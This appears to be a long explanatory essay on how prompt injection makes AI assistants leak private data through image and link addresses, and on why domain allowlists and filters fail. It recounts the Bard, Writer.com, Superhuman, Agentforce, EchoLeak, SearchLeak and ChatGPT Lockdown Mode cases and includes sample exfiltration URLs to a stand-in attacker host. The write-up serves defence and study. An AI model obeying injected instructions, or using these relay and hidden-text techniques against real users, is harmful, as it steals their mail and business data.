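In another of Willison's experiments, the user decided which sites to allow. When the policy blocked a connection, the client showed a box that named the site and offered to add it to the list. If the user agreed, the client reloaded the app with the new entry. This is convenient, and nobody has to predict which sites an app will need. But suppose Ines's assistant makes her a cost calculator and she is asked to approve `https://api.prices.example`. She can't tell from the name who can read what the app sends there. She also wants the calculator to work, so she'll probably click OK, and her approval will cover every later request to that host, whatever data it contains.

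The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a standard for connecting assistants to outside tools and data. Its MCP Apps specification lets a server supply an interface for the assistant to display and declare the domains that the interface needs. The assistant's client turns the declaration into a CSP for the frame. The server's developer knows best which hosts the app uses, and reviewers can check the written declaration before they approve the server. However, this also means that the developer chooses the app's restrictions. The declaration limits the damage if someone else injects code into an honest developer's app, but a dishonest developer can declare a domain that collects data.

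A declaration is therefore best treated as a request. The company that runs the assistant, or the customer's own security team, can keep a list of allowed hosts and add it as a second policy. An app could then reach only the hosts that appear in both its declaration and that list. The model should not influence either one, since a hostile email can affect anything it writes.

### The popup that got around Lockdown Mode

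OpenAI's Lockdown Mode is an optional setting for people who handle sensitive information in ChatGPT. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* explains that it limits or turns off features that connect to outside systems, including live web access, images in answers, file downloads and network requests from Canvas, a workspace for documents and code. OpenAI first released it for large organisations and extended it to personal accounts in June 2026. Willison (2026) inferred from its existence that ChatGPT's normal settings don't reliably stop a determined attacker. OpenAI's head of security, Dane Stuckey, said that it was meant for people at higher risk, for whom the protection was worth the loss of features.

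Researchers at the security company Check Point found a way around ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode. ChatGPT can display a preview of a web page whose code appears in a conversation. According to *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* (Duggan, 2026), OpenAI had contained each preview inside two nested sandboxed frames, and ChatGPT asked the user before letting the page load anything from outside.

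These restrictions didn't cover opening a new window, which loads an address and so can carry data out just as an image can. The sandbox's `allow-popups` setting let the preview open windows, and `allow-popups-to-escape-sandbox` freed those windows from the sandbox's rules. OpenAI had tried to prevent leaks this way with a script that replaced `window.open`, the browser's function for opening windows, with a version that required approval. But every frame has its own copy of that function, so code in the preview could create another frame inside the preview and use the original copy there.

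In a web browser, the user generally had to click something before the window opened. In ChatGPT Classic, a desktop app built on browser technology, the window opened without a click. An attacker could publish a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT with its own instructions, that sent the chat history to the attacker's server while the user was talking to it. The attacker could also fill the window with a fake ChatGPT update or login page.

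OpenAI removed both exceptions from the outer frame by 18 September 2026, and Check Point confirmed that the attack no longer worked. Duggan found no evidence that anyone had used it against real users. The fix is stronger than the earlier block because the browser enforces it. The earlier block was a script running in the same place as the attacker's code, so that code could bypass it. A CSP would not have helped, because it doesn't restrict new windows.

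Another attack on the previews went through the main chat page. OpenAI fixed it on 26 October. In *Do the Math*, Goyal (2026) describes how he and his colleagues at the company Parameter took over the accounts of people who opened a shared ChatGPT conversation containing a graph and a preview. To draw the graph, ChatGPT loaded a mathematics library that also listened for messages about its on-screen keyboard and did not check who sent them. The preview sent the library a new keyboard layout containing HTML. The library put this HTML into the main page, where it created a frame that had no sandbox and counted as part of `chatgpt.com`.

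At that point the main page's CSP blocked the attack because it didn't allow scripts written directly into the page. But it allowed scripts from YouTube, and one YouTube address returned text from the request as part of a script. The researchers used that address to run their own code with the victim's login, and the code could read private conversations. Willison (2026) adds in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts* that the data then left through an image address. Check Point told The Hacker News that the two flaws were separate, although both were in the preview feature (*Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction*, 2026).

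## What happens when an allowed domain accepts data from anyone?

The entry `img.firm.example` in Ines's policy was safe because only her firm could read that server's logs. Suppose the firm moves its pictures to a commercial hosting service and adds `*.bighost.example` to `img-src`. The hosting company is large and reputable, but it rents space to anyone and gives each customer a host name under the domain and a log of the requests to it. The attacker opens an account, receives `x7.bighost.example`, and puts that host in the image address of the next hostile email. Because the host matches the new entry, Ines's browser sends the request, and the attacker reads the price in the log.

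The firm wrongly assumed that if a reputable company owns a domain, only that company can read the requests sent to it. The browser cannot correct this mistake because it only compares domain names and has no information about who operates the servers behind them.

An allowlist entry is safe against leaks only if no outsider can host, log or store anything at any address it matches. An outsider who can host a program there can use it to record incoming requests. An outsider with a customer or analytics account may be able to read a log of requests without running any program. If a service stores what people send it, as an online form does, an outsider may be able to retrieve the data. A wildcard entry must meet this condition for every subdomain, including those the owner adds later.

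Some domains are obviously unsafe to allow. The default allowlist for the browser tool in Google's programming assistant Antigravity included `webhook.site`, a service that records requests. Most cases are harder to judge, and Willison called finding domains that attackers cannot use to collect data "a tricky proposition".

### GitHub's image list

GitHub ran into this problem on ordinary web pages, years before AI assistants. GitHub (2017) describes hiring the security company Cure53 to find out what an attacker could do after inserting HTML into one of its pages. GitHub had already replaced the asterisk in its `img-src` with a short list of allowed domains, including that of Google Analytics, which counts visits to websites.

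Cure53 inserted an image tag with an unclosed quotation mark. The browser treated the HTML that followed, including a secret, as part of the image's address. The address pointed to a Google Analytics account that an attacker could have opened, so the secret would have appeared in the attacker's visitor statistics. According to Detectify (2018), Google doesn't check which site these image requests come from because customers use the images in many places, including emails.

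GitHub responded by using a script to send its visitor statistics, which allowed it to remove Google Analytics from `img-src`. The host remained on the `connect-src` list, but an attacker who can only insert images can't use that. The attacker in Ines's case can also only insert images, but has an advantage over Cure53 because the model can write the secret into the image's address. The attack therefore doesn't depend on a broken tag or on where the secret appears in the page.

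### Google Bard and Apps Script

In 2023 Google gave its chatbot Bard, Gemini's predecessor, access to users' email and documents. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how Rehberger, with Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake, tried the usual image attack. Bard included the image in its answer, but the browser blocked it because the CSP didn't allow Rehberger's server. The policy did allow `*.google.com` and `*.googleusercontent.com`.

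Google also runs Apps Script, where people can write small programs, much like macros in Microsoft Office, and call them through a web address on `script.google.com`. Rehberger wrote a program there that copied the query string of each request into a Google Doc he owned. He found a setting that let visitors use the program without logging in.

Rehberger put the hostile instructions in another Google Doc, which an attacker could share with a victim without the victim's permission. When the user brought that document into the conversation, Bard took the first 20 words of the chat and wrote them into an image address on `script.google.com`. The host matched `*.google.com`, so the browser sent the request. Rehberger needed ten attempts to get the instructions right, because Bard filled in the address correctly only when they included examples.

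Rehberger reported the flaw on 19 September 2023, and Google confirmed on 19 October that it had fixed it. The CSP was unchanged and Bard still displayed images, so he guessed that Google was now filtering out URLs with data in them, but he couldn't confirm this from outside.

Google later chose a simpler rule. According to Google (2025), Gemini recognises external image addresses and does not display images from them. This would stop the Bard attack if Gemini treats an address on `script.google.com` as external. The original policy got this same question about ownership wrong.

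Colab, Google's service for running code in a browser, also relied on this assumption. It showed a confirmation page before opening a link from its AI assistant, but Embrace The Red found that it skipped this page for Google's own domains, so a link to an Apps Script program opened without warning.

### Writer.com and CloudFront

Writer.com, a service that helps companies write documents with AI, had a policy that allowed images from `*.cloudfront.net`. This domain belongs to Amazon's CloudFront, a content delivery network that stores copies of customers' files around the world so that they load quickly. Each customer gets a host name under `cloudfront.net` and can read a log of the requests to it, so the policy let any CloudFront customer receive leaked data. Microsoft's Azure Blob Storage, which later provided a way to get data out of ChatGPT, also lets customers log requests to a shared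 domain.

PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Writer.com via Indirect Prompt Injection* (2023) describes an attack in which a user asks for a report, uploads a file of client data and adds a web page as a source. White text on the page tells the model to include an image whose address contains the file's contents. PromptArmor used a made-up file with names, social security numbers, revenue and salaries, and found all of this data in its own CloudFront log.

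PromptArmor reported the flaw on 29 November 2023. On 5 December Writer.com replied, "We do not consider this to be a security issue", saying that real customer accounts could not access websites. PromptArmor answered that paid accounts had the same flaw, heard nothing more and published its report on 15 December. Four days later, Writer.com no longer displayed images or clickable links in its answers.

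This fix was broader than correcting the list, which would not have stopped data theft through links because `img-src` doesn't cover them. PromptArmor had also extracted files and chat history that way. With neither images nor links, the hosts the policy allowed for images no longer mattered.

### Superhuman and Google Forms

Superhuman, an email app with an AI assistant, allowed a single host, `docs.google.com`, whereas the Bard policy had a wildcard. That host serves Google Docs, but also Google Forms, Google's survey service. Anyone can create a form and read the responses.

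Browsers normally use a GET request to fetch a page or image and a POST request to submit data. Google Forms also accepts responses through GET, so that a form's creator can make a link that submits prefilled answers when opened. If that link is used as the address of an image, the browser submits the form when it loads the image.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* shows how an attacker could exploit this. The attacker sends the victim an email, which the victim doesn't have to open. When the victim asks for a summary of recent mail, the assistant reads the hostile email along with the others. The hostile email says that users must be able to give feedback on the search results, and it gives the address of a Google Form. The assistant adds the contents of the other emails to that address and uses the result as the URL of an image. When the browser tries to load the image, Google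 stores the emails as a form response, which the attacker can read.

PromptArmor extracted the full text of several emails in one answer, including financial, legal and medical information, and parts of more than 40 emails in another. This is far more than the 20 words extracted from Bard, although both attacks put the data in an image address.

PromptArmor sent its report late on Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman turned off the vulnerable features the following Monday and released its first patch on Tuesday. It released more patches until 11 January 2026, the day before the two companies made the flaw public.

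Correcting the entry for `docs.google.com` would not have been enough. Superhuman Go, the same company's assistant for reading web pages and connecting to users' mail, loaded images from the attacker's own domain, so the attacker didn't need a form. Superhuman Mail could also open any web address when it searched for information, and a page's CSP doesn't restrict those requests.

The same attack worked a few months later on Codex, OpenAI's programming agent, which by then also handled email. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* (2026) reports that a hostile message made Codex put other emails into a Google Form through an image. PromptArmor reported the flaw to OpenAI in April 2026, and OpenAI had fixed it by the time the report came out on 21 May. It isn't clear whether Codex restricted image hosts, so the attack may not have bypassed an allowlist. Even without an allowlist to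 bypass, using a form saves an attacker from having to run a server.

### ForcedLeak: an entry that expired

An allowlist entry can pass the test when a developer adds it and fail years later. Salesforce sells customer-tracking software, and its Agentforce product adds AI agents that read the customer records. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reposts the report by Noma Labs, the security team that found this flaw in Agentforce.

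The Agentforce policy had 22 host entries for images. One was `*.my-salesforce-cms.com`, a domain whose registration had lapsed. Noma Labs bought the domain for $5, and requests to it then went to a server that Noma Labs controlled, even though the policy hadn't changed. HTTPS doesn't prevent this, because an ordinary certificate shows that a server's operator controls the domain, and the new owner does.

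The hostile text came in through Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature. When a potential customer (a "lead") fills in a form on a company's website, the feature adds their details to the company's customer records. Most of the form's fields hold between 40 and 80 characters, but the description field holds 42,000, enough for a set of instructions. An employee later asked Agentforce to look at the lead and answer the person's questions. Agentforce also looked up the email addresses of the company's other leads and wrote them into the URL of an image on the expired domain.

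Only companies that used Web-to-Lead were vulnerable, according to *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection* (Paganini, 2025). The demonstrated attack stole email addresses, but Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* also lists sales plans and internal communications among the data at risk.

Noma Labs may not have needed the expired domain. The allowlist also contained `*.amazonaws.com`, which Amazon's customers use for storage and other services, and `*.cloudinary.com`, which belongs to an image-hosting company. Both companies serve outside customers from these domains, so both entries look similar to Writer.com's `*.cloudfront.net`. Noma Labs didn't test them, but if an attacker could have read requests sent to either one, renewing the expired domain would not have closed the leak.

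### Salesforce's fix

Noma Labs reported the flaw on 28 July 2025. Salesforce took back control of the domain and, according to Willison, audited and corrected its CSP before adding a second check called Trusted URLs. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* (2025) gives 8 September as the date the check became mandatory, 17 days before Noma Labs published its findings.

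In Salesforce's web app, the Trusted URLs output filter replaces any address that isn't on the customer's list with `[URL_REDACTED]` before the browser displays the answer. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* explains that the filter covers images, links, and addresses inside HTML and style sheets. An administrator can also choose what each entry is for, such as allowing links to a supplier's website but not images from it.

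The filter doesn't cover actions an agent takes with its tools, such as sending an email. PromptArmor recommends human approval for those actions. It also advises administrators to avoid wildcards that include sites with user-generated content, and to turn off images for each entry unless they need them.

This advice matters because Trusted URLs relies on each customer's administrator to apply the test. If an administrator leaves out a domain that an agent needs, its links stop working and employees will probably complain, but if they add `*.cloudfront.net`, everything works and nobody notices the risk. The list that draws the fewest complaints is therefore likely to be too broad.

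### What would have prevented these leaks?

The most obvious remedy is to replace wildcards with exact host names, but it would have helped in only two of the four cases:

| Product | Entry in the policy | Who could read requests there | Would exact host names have helped? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bard | `*.google.com` | Anyone with an Apps Script program | Yes, if the list left out `script.google.com` |
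| Writer.com | `*.cloudfront.net` | Any CloudFront customer | Yes, if it listed only Writer.com's own host |
| Superhuman | `docs.google.com` | Anyone with a Google Form | No, the entry was already an exact host |
| Agentforce | `*.my-salesforce-cms.com` | Whoever registered the expired domain | No, the new owner controlled every host under it |

Superhuman could have added a path to its allowlist entry so that the entry matched documents but not forms. But a redirect from any other listed host would have bypassed that restriction, because browsers ignore the paths in allowlist entries after a redirect.

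Google could have solved Superhuman's problem by moving Forms to a separate domain. If a company keeps its own pages and its users' content on different domains, other websites can allow the company's pages without allowing the users' content. Google hosts much of its users' content on `googleusercontent.com`. But separation only helps if the people writing policies know what each domain is for, and Bard's own policy allowed both. It also requires the host's owner to act, and the owner may see no reason to, since a form that accepts answers through a link is working as intended. The form becomes a security problem only when someone else's policy treats the host as private.

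Agentforce lacked a regular check of its allowlist. Software can look up when each domain's registration expires and warn the owner in time, and developers can delete entries that their product no longer uses. CSP's violation reports won't reveal a lapsed domain, because the browser doesn't block requests to a listed host. An expiry check finds only expired or expiring registrations, though, so it would not have flagged `*.amazonaws.com`.

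Blocking all external images would have stopped all four attacks. With `img-src 'self'`, the developer only has to examine the page's own server and can usually find out who reads its logs. That server must still pass the test, and it could fail if it also runs users' programs or stores their forms.

The drawback is that the assistant can't show pictures from the web unless they are first copied to its own server. For many assistants this is a small loss. It is a bigger problem for an email app, because ordinary messages are full of images from other companies' servers. The app's developer could display the assistant's answers in a separate frame with a stricter policy than the one for messages.

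### Evidence from script policies

Researchers had already shown that host allowlists fail at CSP's original job of blocking an attacker's scripts. Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues searched Google's index of about 106 billion web pages and found 26,011 different policies (*CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!*, 2016). An attacker who could insert HTML into the page could easily get around 94.72% of them.

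That figure by itself is weak evidence about allowlists, because 84.38% of the policies used a setting that lets scripts written directly into the page run, which makes the choice of listed hosts matter little. The 2,437 stricter policies, which had neither that setting nor a wildcard for all hosts, are better evidence. Of these, 41.65% still listed at least one host that an attacker could use to run a script.

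Weichselbaum and colleagues looked for two common features that make a host unsafe. They found 194,908 domains that return a script containing text from the request, which lets an attacker write part of the script. They also found 101,330 domains that store a copy of AngularJS, a library that can run instructions it finds in a page's HTML. They regard these counts as a lower limit because their automated search covered only these two features.

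Of the 15 hosts that appeared most often in script lists, 14 offered a way around the policy, though two of them did so only if the policy also allowed a risky JavaScript function. One of the 14, `*.google.com`, appeared in 22.36% of the policies and was the entry that later let data out of Bard. Longer lists were easier to bypass. The median policy named 12 hosts, and the researchers could bypass 94.8% of the policies of that length.

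Google had trouble with its own lists, too. Developers on one part of Google Maps introduced a careful policy in February 2015 and had to make five major changes to it that year. The policy grew to 15 long entries, including at least one unsafe entry that the product required.

These percentages don't apply to images, because a script attack depends on what the host sends back to the browser, whereas an image leak depends on who can read the request. The YouTube address in the attack on ChatGPT's previews was dangerous in a script list, but that doesn't mean an outsider could read YouTube's logs. Google Analytics is nearly the reverse, since as a script source it was one of the two hosts that needed the risky function, but as an image source it delivered data to anyone with an account.

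The difficulty of maintaining a list does carry over. A developer has to know about every service on every listed host, and the companies that run those hosts don't know that someone else's security depends on them. Agentforce's 22 image hosts would have been a lot to check even if none had expired.

Weichselbaum and colleagues concluded that developers should stop listing hosts for scripts and approve each script individually. Each time the page loads, the server generates a random code, called a nonce, and puts it in both the policy and the tag of every legitimate script. An attacker can't guess the code, so the browser won't run an inserted script even if it comes from a popular host.

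CSP has no nonces for images, but GitHub built something similar for profile pictures. These came from Gravatar, another host that Cure53 had used to get data out. GitHub now fetches them through its own image proxy, Camo, which accepts an address only with a valid signature, a code that GitHub's server calculates from the full address and a secret key. The server has each picture's address before it builds the page, so it can sign it in advance. An attacker who adds stolen data to the address can't produce a matching signature. The protection depends on which addresses the server signs. If the software behind Ines's assistant signed every image address in the model's answer, it would also sign the one containing her firm's price.

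## What happens when an allowed domain redirects or fetches other addresses?

A listed host can leak data even if no outsider can read its logs, because it may pass a request on to another server. Suppose `www.maps.example` matches the entry `*.maps.example` in the policy of Ines's firm, and only the map supplier's staff can read that host's logs. The supplier's website has two ordinary features: one forwards visitors to other sites to count clicks on its links, and the other previews any web page whose address a visitor enters. Both accept an outside address as part of the request, and an attacker can get the assistant to write the firm's price into that address.

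A CSP stops a leak through the forwarding page but not one through the preview page, though reports of attacks often treat these two features as the same flaw.

### Who sends the second request?

If the assistant's answer contains an image at the forwarding page, its address might be:

`https://www.maps.example/go?to=https://img.attacker.example/4.18m.png`

1. Ines's browser finds that `www.maps.example` matches the policy and sends the request.
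2. The supplier's server replies with a redirect to `img.attacker.example`.
3. The browser compares the new host with the policy, finds no match and stops.

The price has reached the map supplier but not the attacker. With the preview page, the address looks almost the same:

`https://www.maps.example/preview?url=https://img.attacker.example/4.18m.png`

1. Ines's browser again finds a match and sends the request.
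2. The supplier's server requests the image from `img.attacker.example`, and the attacker's log now contains the price.
3. The supplier's server returns a preview or an error message to the browser.

This is a server-side fetch. Ines's browser made only one request, to a listed host, so it had nothing to block.

| | Redirect | Server-side fetch |
|---|---|---|
| Who contacts the attacker's server? | The user's browser | The listed site's server |
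| Whose network address is in the attacker's log? | The user's | The listed site's |
| Does the page's CSP check that request? | Yes | No |
| Does a filter that reads only the first host stop it? | No | No |

In 2013 an engineer at Twitter was puzzled that a browser's check on redirects flagged `www.google.com` when his test page mentioned only `google.com`. Veditz (2013), who worked at Mozilla, explained that CSP applies to where content comes from, not to the text of the page, so a policy has to list every host in a chain of redirects. If browsers checked only the addresses written in the page, he wrote, an open redirect on any listed site would completely negate the policy.

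The next year West raised the "nuclear option" of checking only the first address. This would have stopped hostile pages from learning about visitors through blocked redirects, but he noted that it would also weaken policies. W3C instead kept checking the host after a redirect and dropped only the path check. A browser test in Searchfox, Mozilla's code index, loads an image that redirects away from the permitted server. Browsers that display the image fail the test.

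A developer can easily misread the resulting violation report. According to W3C, the report gives the address originally requested and omits the redirect's destination, which might include private information. The developer therefore sees a violation reported for an address that the policy appears to allow.

### Bing's search links in ChatGPT

Filters that check only the first address don't protect against redirects. ChatGPT sends most addresses in its answers to an OpenAI service called `url_safe`, which decides whether to display them. *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025), by the security company Tenable, reports that this service always approved addresses on `bing.com`. Bing's search results link to other websites through `bing.com` tracking links that redirect to them, so every site in Bing's index has a `bing.com` address that leads to it.

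An attacker can't add stolen data to one of these links, because Bing generates them and any change breaks them. In Tenable's *HackedGPT* (2025), researchers got around this by having Bing index a separate page for each letter of the alphabet, then making ChatGPT display images using the matching links in order. Sending "Hello" took five images. Ines's price, `4.18m`, would also take five, with extra pages for the digits and the decimal point.

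This is slow, but the researchers also planted an instruction in ChatGPT's memory, which it uses in every conversation, so each later answer leaked more data. A CSP that allowed `bing.com` but not the researchers' sites would have blocked the images at the second request.

Tenable reported the flaw on 10 December 2024 and had asked for updates six times by 4 March 2025. OpenAI had not fixed it when Tenable published its advisory. The November 2025 report includes a successful test with GPT-5, though by then OpenAI had fixed some of the other flaws in the report.

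### EchoLeak: an email that reached Copilot

Microsoft 365 Copilot, the version for organisations, searches a user's mailbox, chats and files for material related to a question and adds what it finds to the model's input. Only employees can use it, but an outsider can get text into that input by emailing one of them. The EchoLeak attack needed just one such email. Aim Labs, the research team of the security company Aim Security, discovered it in January 2025, and it was later listed as CVE-2025-32711 in the public catalogue of software flaws. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) describes how the attack got past four protections.

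Microsoft had trained a classifier to recognise prompt injection and keep it away from the model. The researchers worded their email as instructions to the employee who received it and never mentioned AI or Copilot, and the classifier let it through. Ravia argues that such classifiers are hard to train because good collections of real attacks are scarce and an attack can cover any subject in any language.

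Copilot also had to retrieve the email when the employee asked a question. Such search systems often split long documents into pieces, convert each piece into numbers that represent its meaning, and find the pieces closest to the question. The researchers considered scrambling characters in copies of their instructions so that the copies would match a wider range of questions. In a trial with one of OpenAI's conversion models, this reduced the similarity between a text and its scrambled copy to as little as 0.7, lower than the score for greeting cards and the philosophy of science. But they didn't know which model Microsoft used, so they took the simpler approach of writing one long email that repeated the instructions under headings about common office topics, such as leave and the induction of new staff. Copilot then retrieved the email for questions on various subjects.

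The instructions told the reader to put the most sensitive information available in a web address. Copilot's output filter removed ordinary markdown links and images that pointed outside the organisation. However, markdown also has a reference style, which puts the address on a separate line. For example, the text contains `![logo][pic]`, and another line contains `[pic]: https://site.example/logo.png`. The filter didn't recognise this form, so Copilot's answer could include an image with the researchers' address.

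The image still failed to load, because the page's CSP didn't allow the researchers' server.

### The Teams preview service

Ravia published the full list of image sources in Copilot's policy. The list had 29 different entries, 11 of them with wildcards. Fourteen entries appeared twice, perhaps because someone had merged several lists. The researchers searched these hosts for one that would contact their server.

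They began with SharePoint, Microsoft's service for internal websites, because the policy allowed `*.sharepoint.com` and an attacker can open a site there. Microsoft no longer let site owners run their own server code, so the researchers couldn't record requests the way Rehberger had with Apps Script. But SharePoint had a service that fetched outside pages to embed them, and it accepted any address. The attack worked only if the victim was logged in to SharePoint and had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site.

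Microsoft Teams had a similar service that required no invitation, on a host that matched `*.teams.microsoft.com`. The image address pointed to this service and contained the researchers' address with the stolen data appended. The employee's browser contacted Teams, as the policy allowed, and Teams then requested the researchers' address.

Copilot normally lists the documents an answer draws on. The email included an instruction never to mention it, supposedly for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it off the list. According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), the employee would have noticed at most what looked like a broken image.

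Aim reported the attack to Microsoft in January. Aim's co-founder Adir Gruss said that Microsoft attempted a fix in April and found further problems in May (Goldman, 2025, *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*). Reddy and Gujral date the completed fix to May. Microsoft made it on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. The details became public on 11 June. Gruss considered five months very long for a flaw like this.

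Microsoft told Goldman that the flaw had not affected any customers, and heise online's *Critical vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot shows risk of AI agents* also reports the company's statement that nobody had exploited it. Microsoft was in a good position to check, since leaks by either route would have passed through its own servers.

### Was it a redirect or a proxy?

On the day of publication, Willison described the Teams address as an open redirect, which he said was all an attacker needed to avoid the CSP. Reddy and Gujral call it a proxy that retrieved the attacker's address for the browser.

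The evidence suggests that Teams acted as a proxy. If it had redirected the browser, the browser would have checked the attacker's host against Copilot's policy and blocked the request. Ravia writes that the SharePoint service makes a request "on behalf of the client" and that the Teams address had the same outcome. He also dismisses redirects as useless for this attack, but his reason is slightly wrong. Browsers do follow redirects when loading images, but only to hosts that the policy allows.

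Reddy and Gujral worked from published accounts and didn't repeat the attack. They don't say whether the attacker's log would show the network address of Microsoft's servers or of the victim. The victim's address would suggest a redirect. Their word "proxy" is therefore weaker evidence than the way browsers enforce CSP.

The difference between a redirect and a fetch by an allowed server affects how developers respond to an attack and how they detect one. Someone who thinks EchoLeak used a redirect might search the listed hosts for open redirects, find none and decide that the list is safe. Or they might conclude that CSP doesn't check redirects and rely on an output filter, which is usually worse at catching them. If Ines's firm records its outgoing traffic, a redirect that got through would appear as a connection to the attacker's server, but a fetch by Teams would appear only as a connection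 to Microsoft.

### A relay that Microsoft knew about

Four years before EchoLeak, *MS Teams* (2021), by the security company Positive Security, found that Microsoft's servers fetched the pages previewed in Teams and did not restrict which addresses they would contact. Microsoft had a good reason to fetch preview pictures itself, since this hid the reader's network address from the other website. In EchoLeak, the same feature became a way to steal data from Copilot.

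The address Positive Security tested and the one in EchoLeak both had paths beginning with `/urlp/v1/url/`, so they were probably parts of the same service. But Positive Security was worried about a different danger, server-side request forgery, in which an outsider gets a server to send requests the outsider couldn't send directly. The usual concern is that the server will reach private machines inside its owner's network. Microsoft closed the report on 25 March 2021, saying it would not fix the problem in the current version.

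The standard protection against that danger is for proxies to refuse to contact private network addresses, which Reddy and Gujral recommend among other precautions. This protects Microsoft's internal machines, but it would not have stopped EchoLeak, because Copilot's data went to an ordinary server on the public internet.

### SearchLeak: the same policy a year later

The policy that Ravia published in 2025 also allowed `*.bing.com`. On 15 June 2026, Varonis' *SearchLeak* described an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that used this entry.

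As in the Reprompt attack, the attacker put instructions for Copilot in a link, this time to Copilot's search page, and Copilot followed them as soon as the victim clicked the link. The link led to a real Microsoft site, so there was no reason for tools that block suspicious links to stop it. Copilot searched the victim's mailbox and put the subject line of an email in the address of an image. In Varonis's example, the subject line contained a security code, which an attacker could use to log in to another service.

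Microsoft had a safeguard that turned any HTML in an answer into harmless text, but it ran only after Copilot had finished writing. Like GitLab Duo, Copilot displayed its answers as it wrote them, so the browser requested the image before the safeguard ran.

The CSP still prevented the browser from contacting the attacker's server directly. Varonis used Bing's image search, which can take the web address of a picture and find similar ones. The image URL in Copilot's answer pointed to this feature on `www.bing.com` and contained the address of a picture on the attacker's server, with the email's subject line in that address's path. The browser sent the request to Bing, whose server tried to download the picture to analyse it. The subject line then appeared in the attacker's log.

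Varonis's account supports its argument that the attack needed every step. If the safeguard had run before display, the browser would never have requested the image. If the policy had left out Bing, it would have blocked the request.

Microsoft patched the flaw, CVE-2026-42824, earlier in June, according to TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool*. WinBuzzer's *Microsoft Patches Copilot SearchLeak Data-Theft Flaw* (2026) reports that there was no public evidence that anyone had exploited it when Varonis published.

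In 2023, Embrace The Red found that Bing Chat's policy already allowed images from four hosts, including `www.bing.com`. The same trick may not have worked then, since image search may have behaved differently. But Microsoft's assistants kept allowing the host for three years. It looked safe because Microsoft owned it, yet it was as useful to an attacker as a rented server.

### How well do the repairs work?

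The owner of the relay can fix it. Teams could fetch a preview only if the request carried a signature that its server had issued when someone posted the link, much as GitHub's image proxy, Camo, accepts only signed addresses. Bing can't do this, because its image search has to accept pictures from anywhere. It could instead refuse requests from images on another company's or product's pages, since browsers include this information in their requests. A fix at the relay protects every product that allows the host, but it leaves all other relays in place, so closing the one in Teams didn't protect Copilot from the one in Bing.

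Removing the host from the policy works whatever the relay does, and the assistant's developer can do it without waiting for another team. However, legitimate pictures from that host also disappear. A developer can often reduce this loss by replacing a wildcard with a host that only serves stored pictures and never fetches anything. Narrowing the entry to a path is less reliable, because a redirect on another listed host could still lead to the relay.

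The remaining option is to check the whole address before displaying the content. In both EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the attacker's address was nested inside an address on a Microsoft host. An output filter that rejected nested addresses would have stopped both attacks if it recognised every markdown notation and ran before the browser displayed anything. CSP can't do this because it ignores query strings. The filter has to decode the address first, since an attacker can disguise the nested part. It will also block some legitimate images, such as those from services that resize pictures from other sites.

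Some addresses, such as short links, may contain only an identifier that the server looks up, so the filter can't read the destination from the address. Reddy and Gujral suggest that the filter expand redirects and verify where they lead before the client displays a link. The filter should follow redirects one at a time and stop before it contacts an unlisted host, because its own request could deliver the data to the attacker.

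A filter can itself cause a leak when it checks whether an address redirects, because it has to request the address. If the address belongs to a relay like the one in Teams, that request makes the relay contact the attacker. The relay's reply contains no redirect, so the filter approves an address that has already leaked the data. The filter should therefore look for nested addresses before it requests anything. For redirects, the browser's own check is better because it happens at each step as the image loads and can't go out of date if someone changes a link's destination.

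### Why a developer may not know about a relay

Varonis advises companies to review their policies for domains that fetch addresses supplied by users. This is difficult because a policy lists hosts, while the fetching feature belongs to one page on a host. Link previews, image searches, web page translators and tools that import files from a web address all make server-side fetches, which their operators consider the purpose of the service rather than a flaw.

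Documentation may not help either. Ravia's team found the SharePoint and Teams services only after what he calls "tedious digging", and Gruss told Goldman that they spent about three months working out how Copilot functioned. If the allowlist has an entry such as `*.bing.com`, another team at the company can also later add a relay without knowing that Copilot's policy covers its host.

Microsoft owned the assistant and both relays, and the 2021 report about Teams was public. Whoever assessed that report was judging a preview feature in a chat app, years before Copilot's policy made it possible to use the feature to take data from people's mailboxes. Gruss said that part of the delay in fixing EchoLeak came from finding the right teams within Microsoft. A smaller company that allowlists another firm's hosts is even less likely to hear about a new feature on them.

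Such a company can at least test for relays. Its developers can set up their own web server, enter its address into every feature of a listed host that takes an address, and watch for a request from the host's servers, which would reveal a relay. If no request arrives, a relay is less likely but still possible, because the developers may have missed a feature. A host with many features is therefore a poor choice for the list even if it passes the test.

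## Does approving exact URLs close the gap that approving domains leaves?

In all the leaks through allowed domains, private data went into an address that passed because its host was on the list. An exact-URL check approves complete addresses one by one, so adding even one character to an approved address means it needs its own approval.

Suppose the software behind Ines's assistant had approved only one address on the map supplier's host, the preview page at `https://www.maps.example/preview?url=https://site.example/plan.png`. A hostile email could still make the assistant request it, but the request would contain only text that existed before the assistant read the bid. It would no longer matter who can read the host's logs, or whether the host redirects the request or fetches another page.

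Deciding which addresses to approve is difficult. A developer can list hosts by hand, but an assistant that browses the web needs a huge number of addresses that nobody can predict. OpenAI and Anthropic therefore automate the decision. OpenAI's software checks whether an address was already public, and Anthropic's checks whether it came from a source other than the model.

### ChatGPT's `url_safe` check

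OpenAI's first attempt was `url_safe`, which it added in December 2023 to check image addresses before ChatGPT displayed them.

Rehberger tested OpenAI's check on the day he noticed it. It rejected a URL with an email address in the query string. He then prepared 36 image URLs, one for each letter and digit, and Embrace The Red reports that nine passed. The URL for "a" was judged safe but the one for "d" was not, for no reason he could see. The check ran on OpenAI's servers, so researchers had to guess its rules, whereas anyone can read a CSP in their browser. Rehberger wondered whether OpenAI was looking URLs up in Bing's index, and hoped it wasn't relying on a language model alone.

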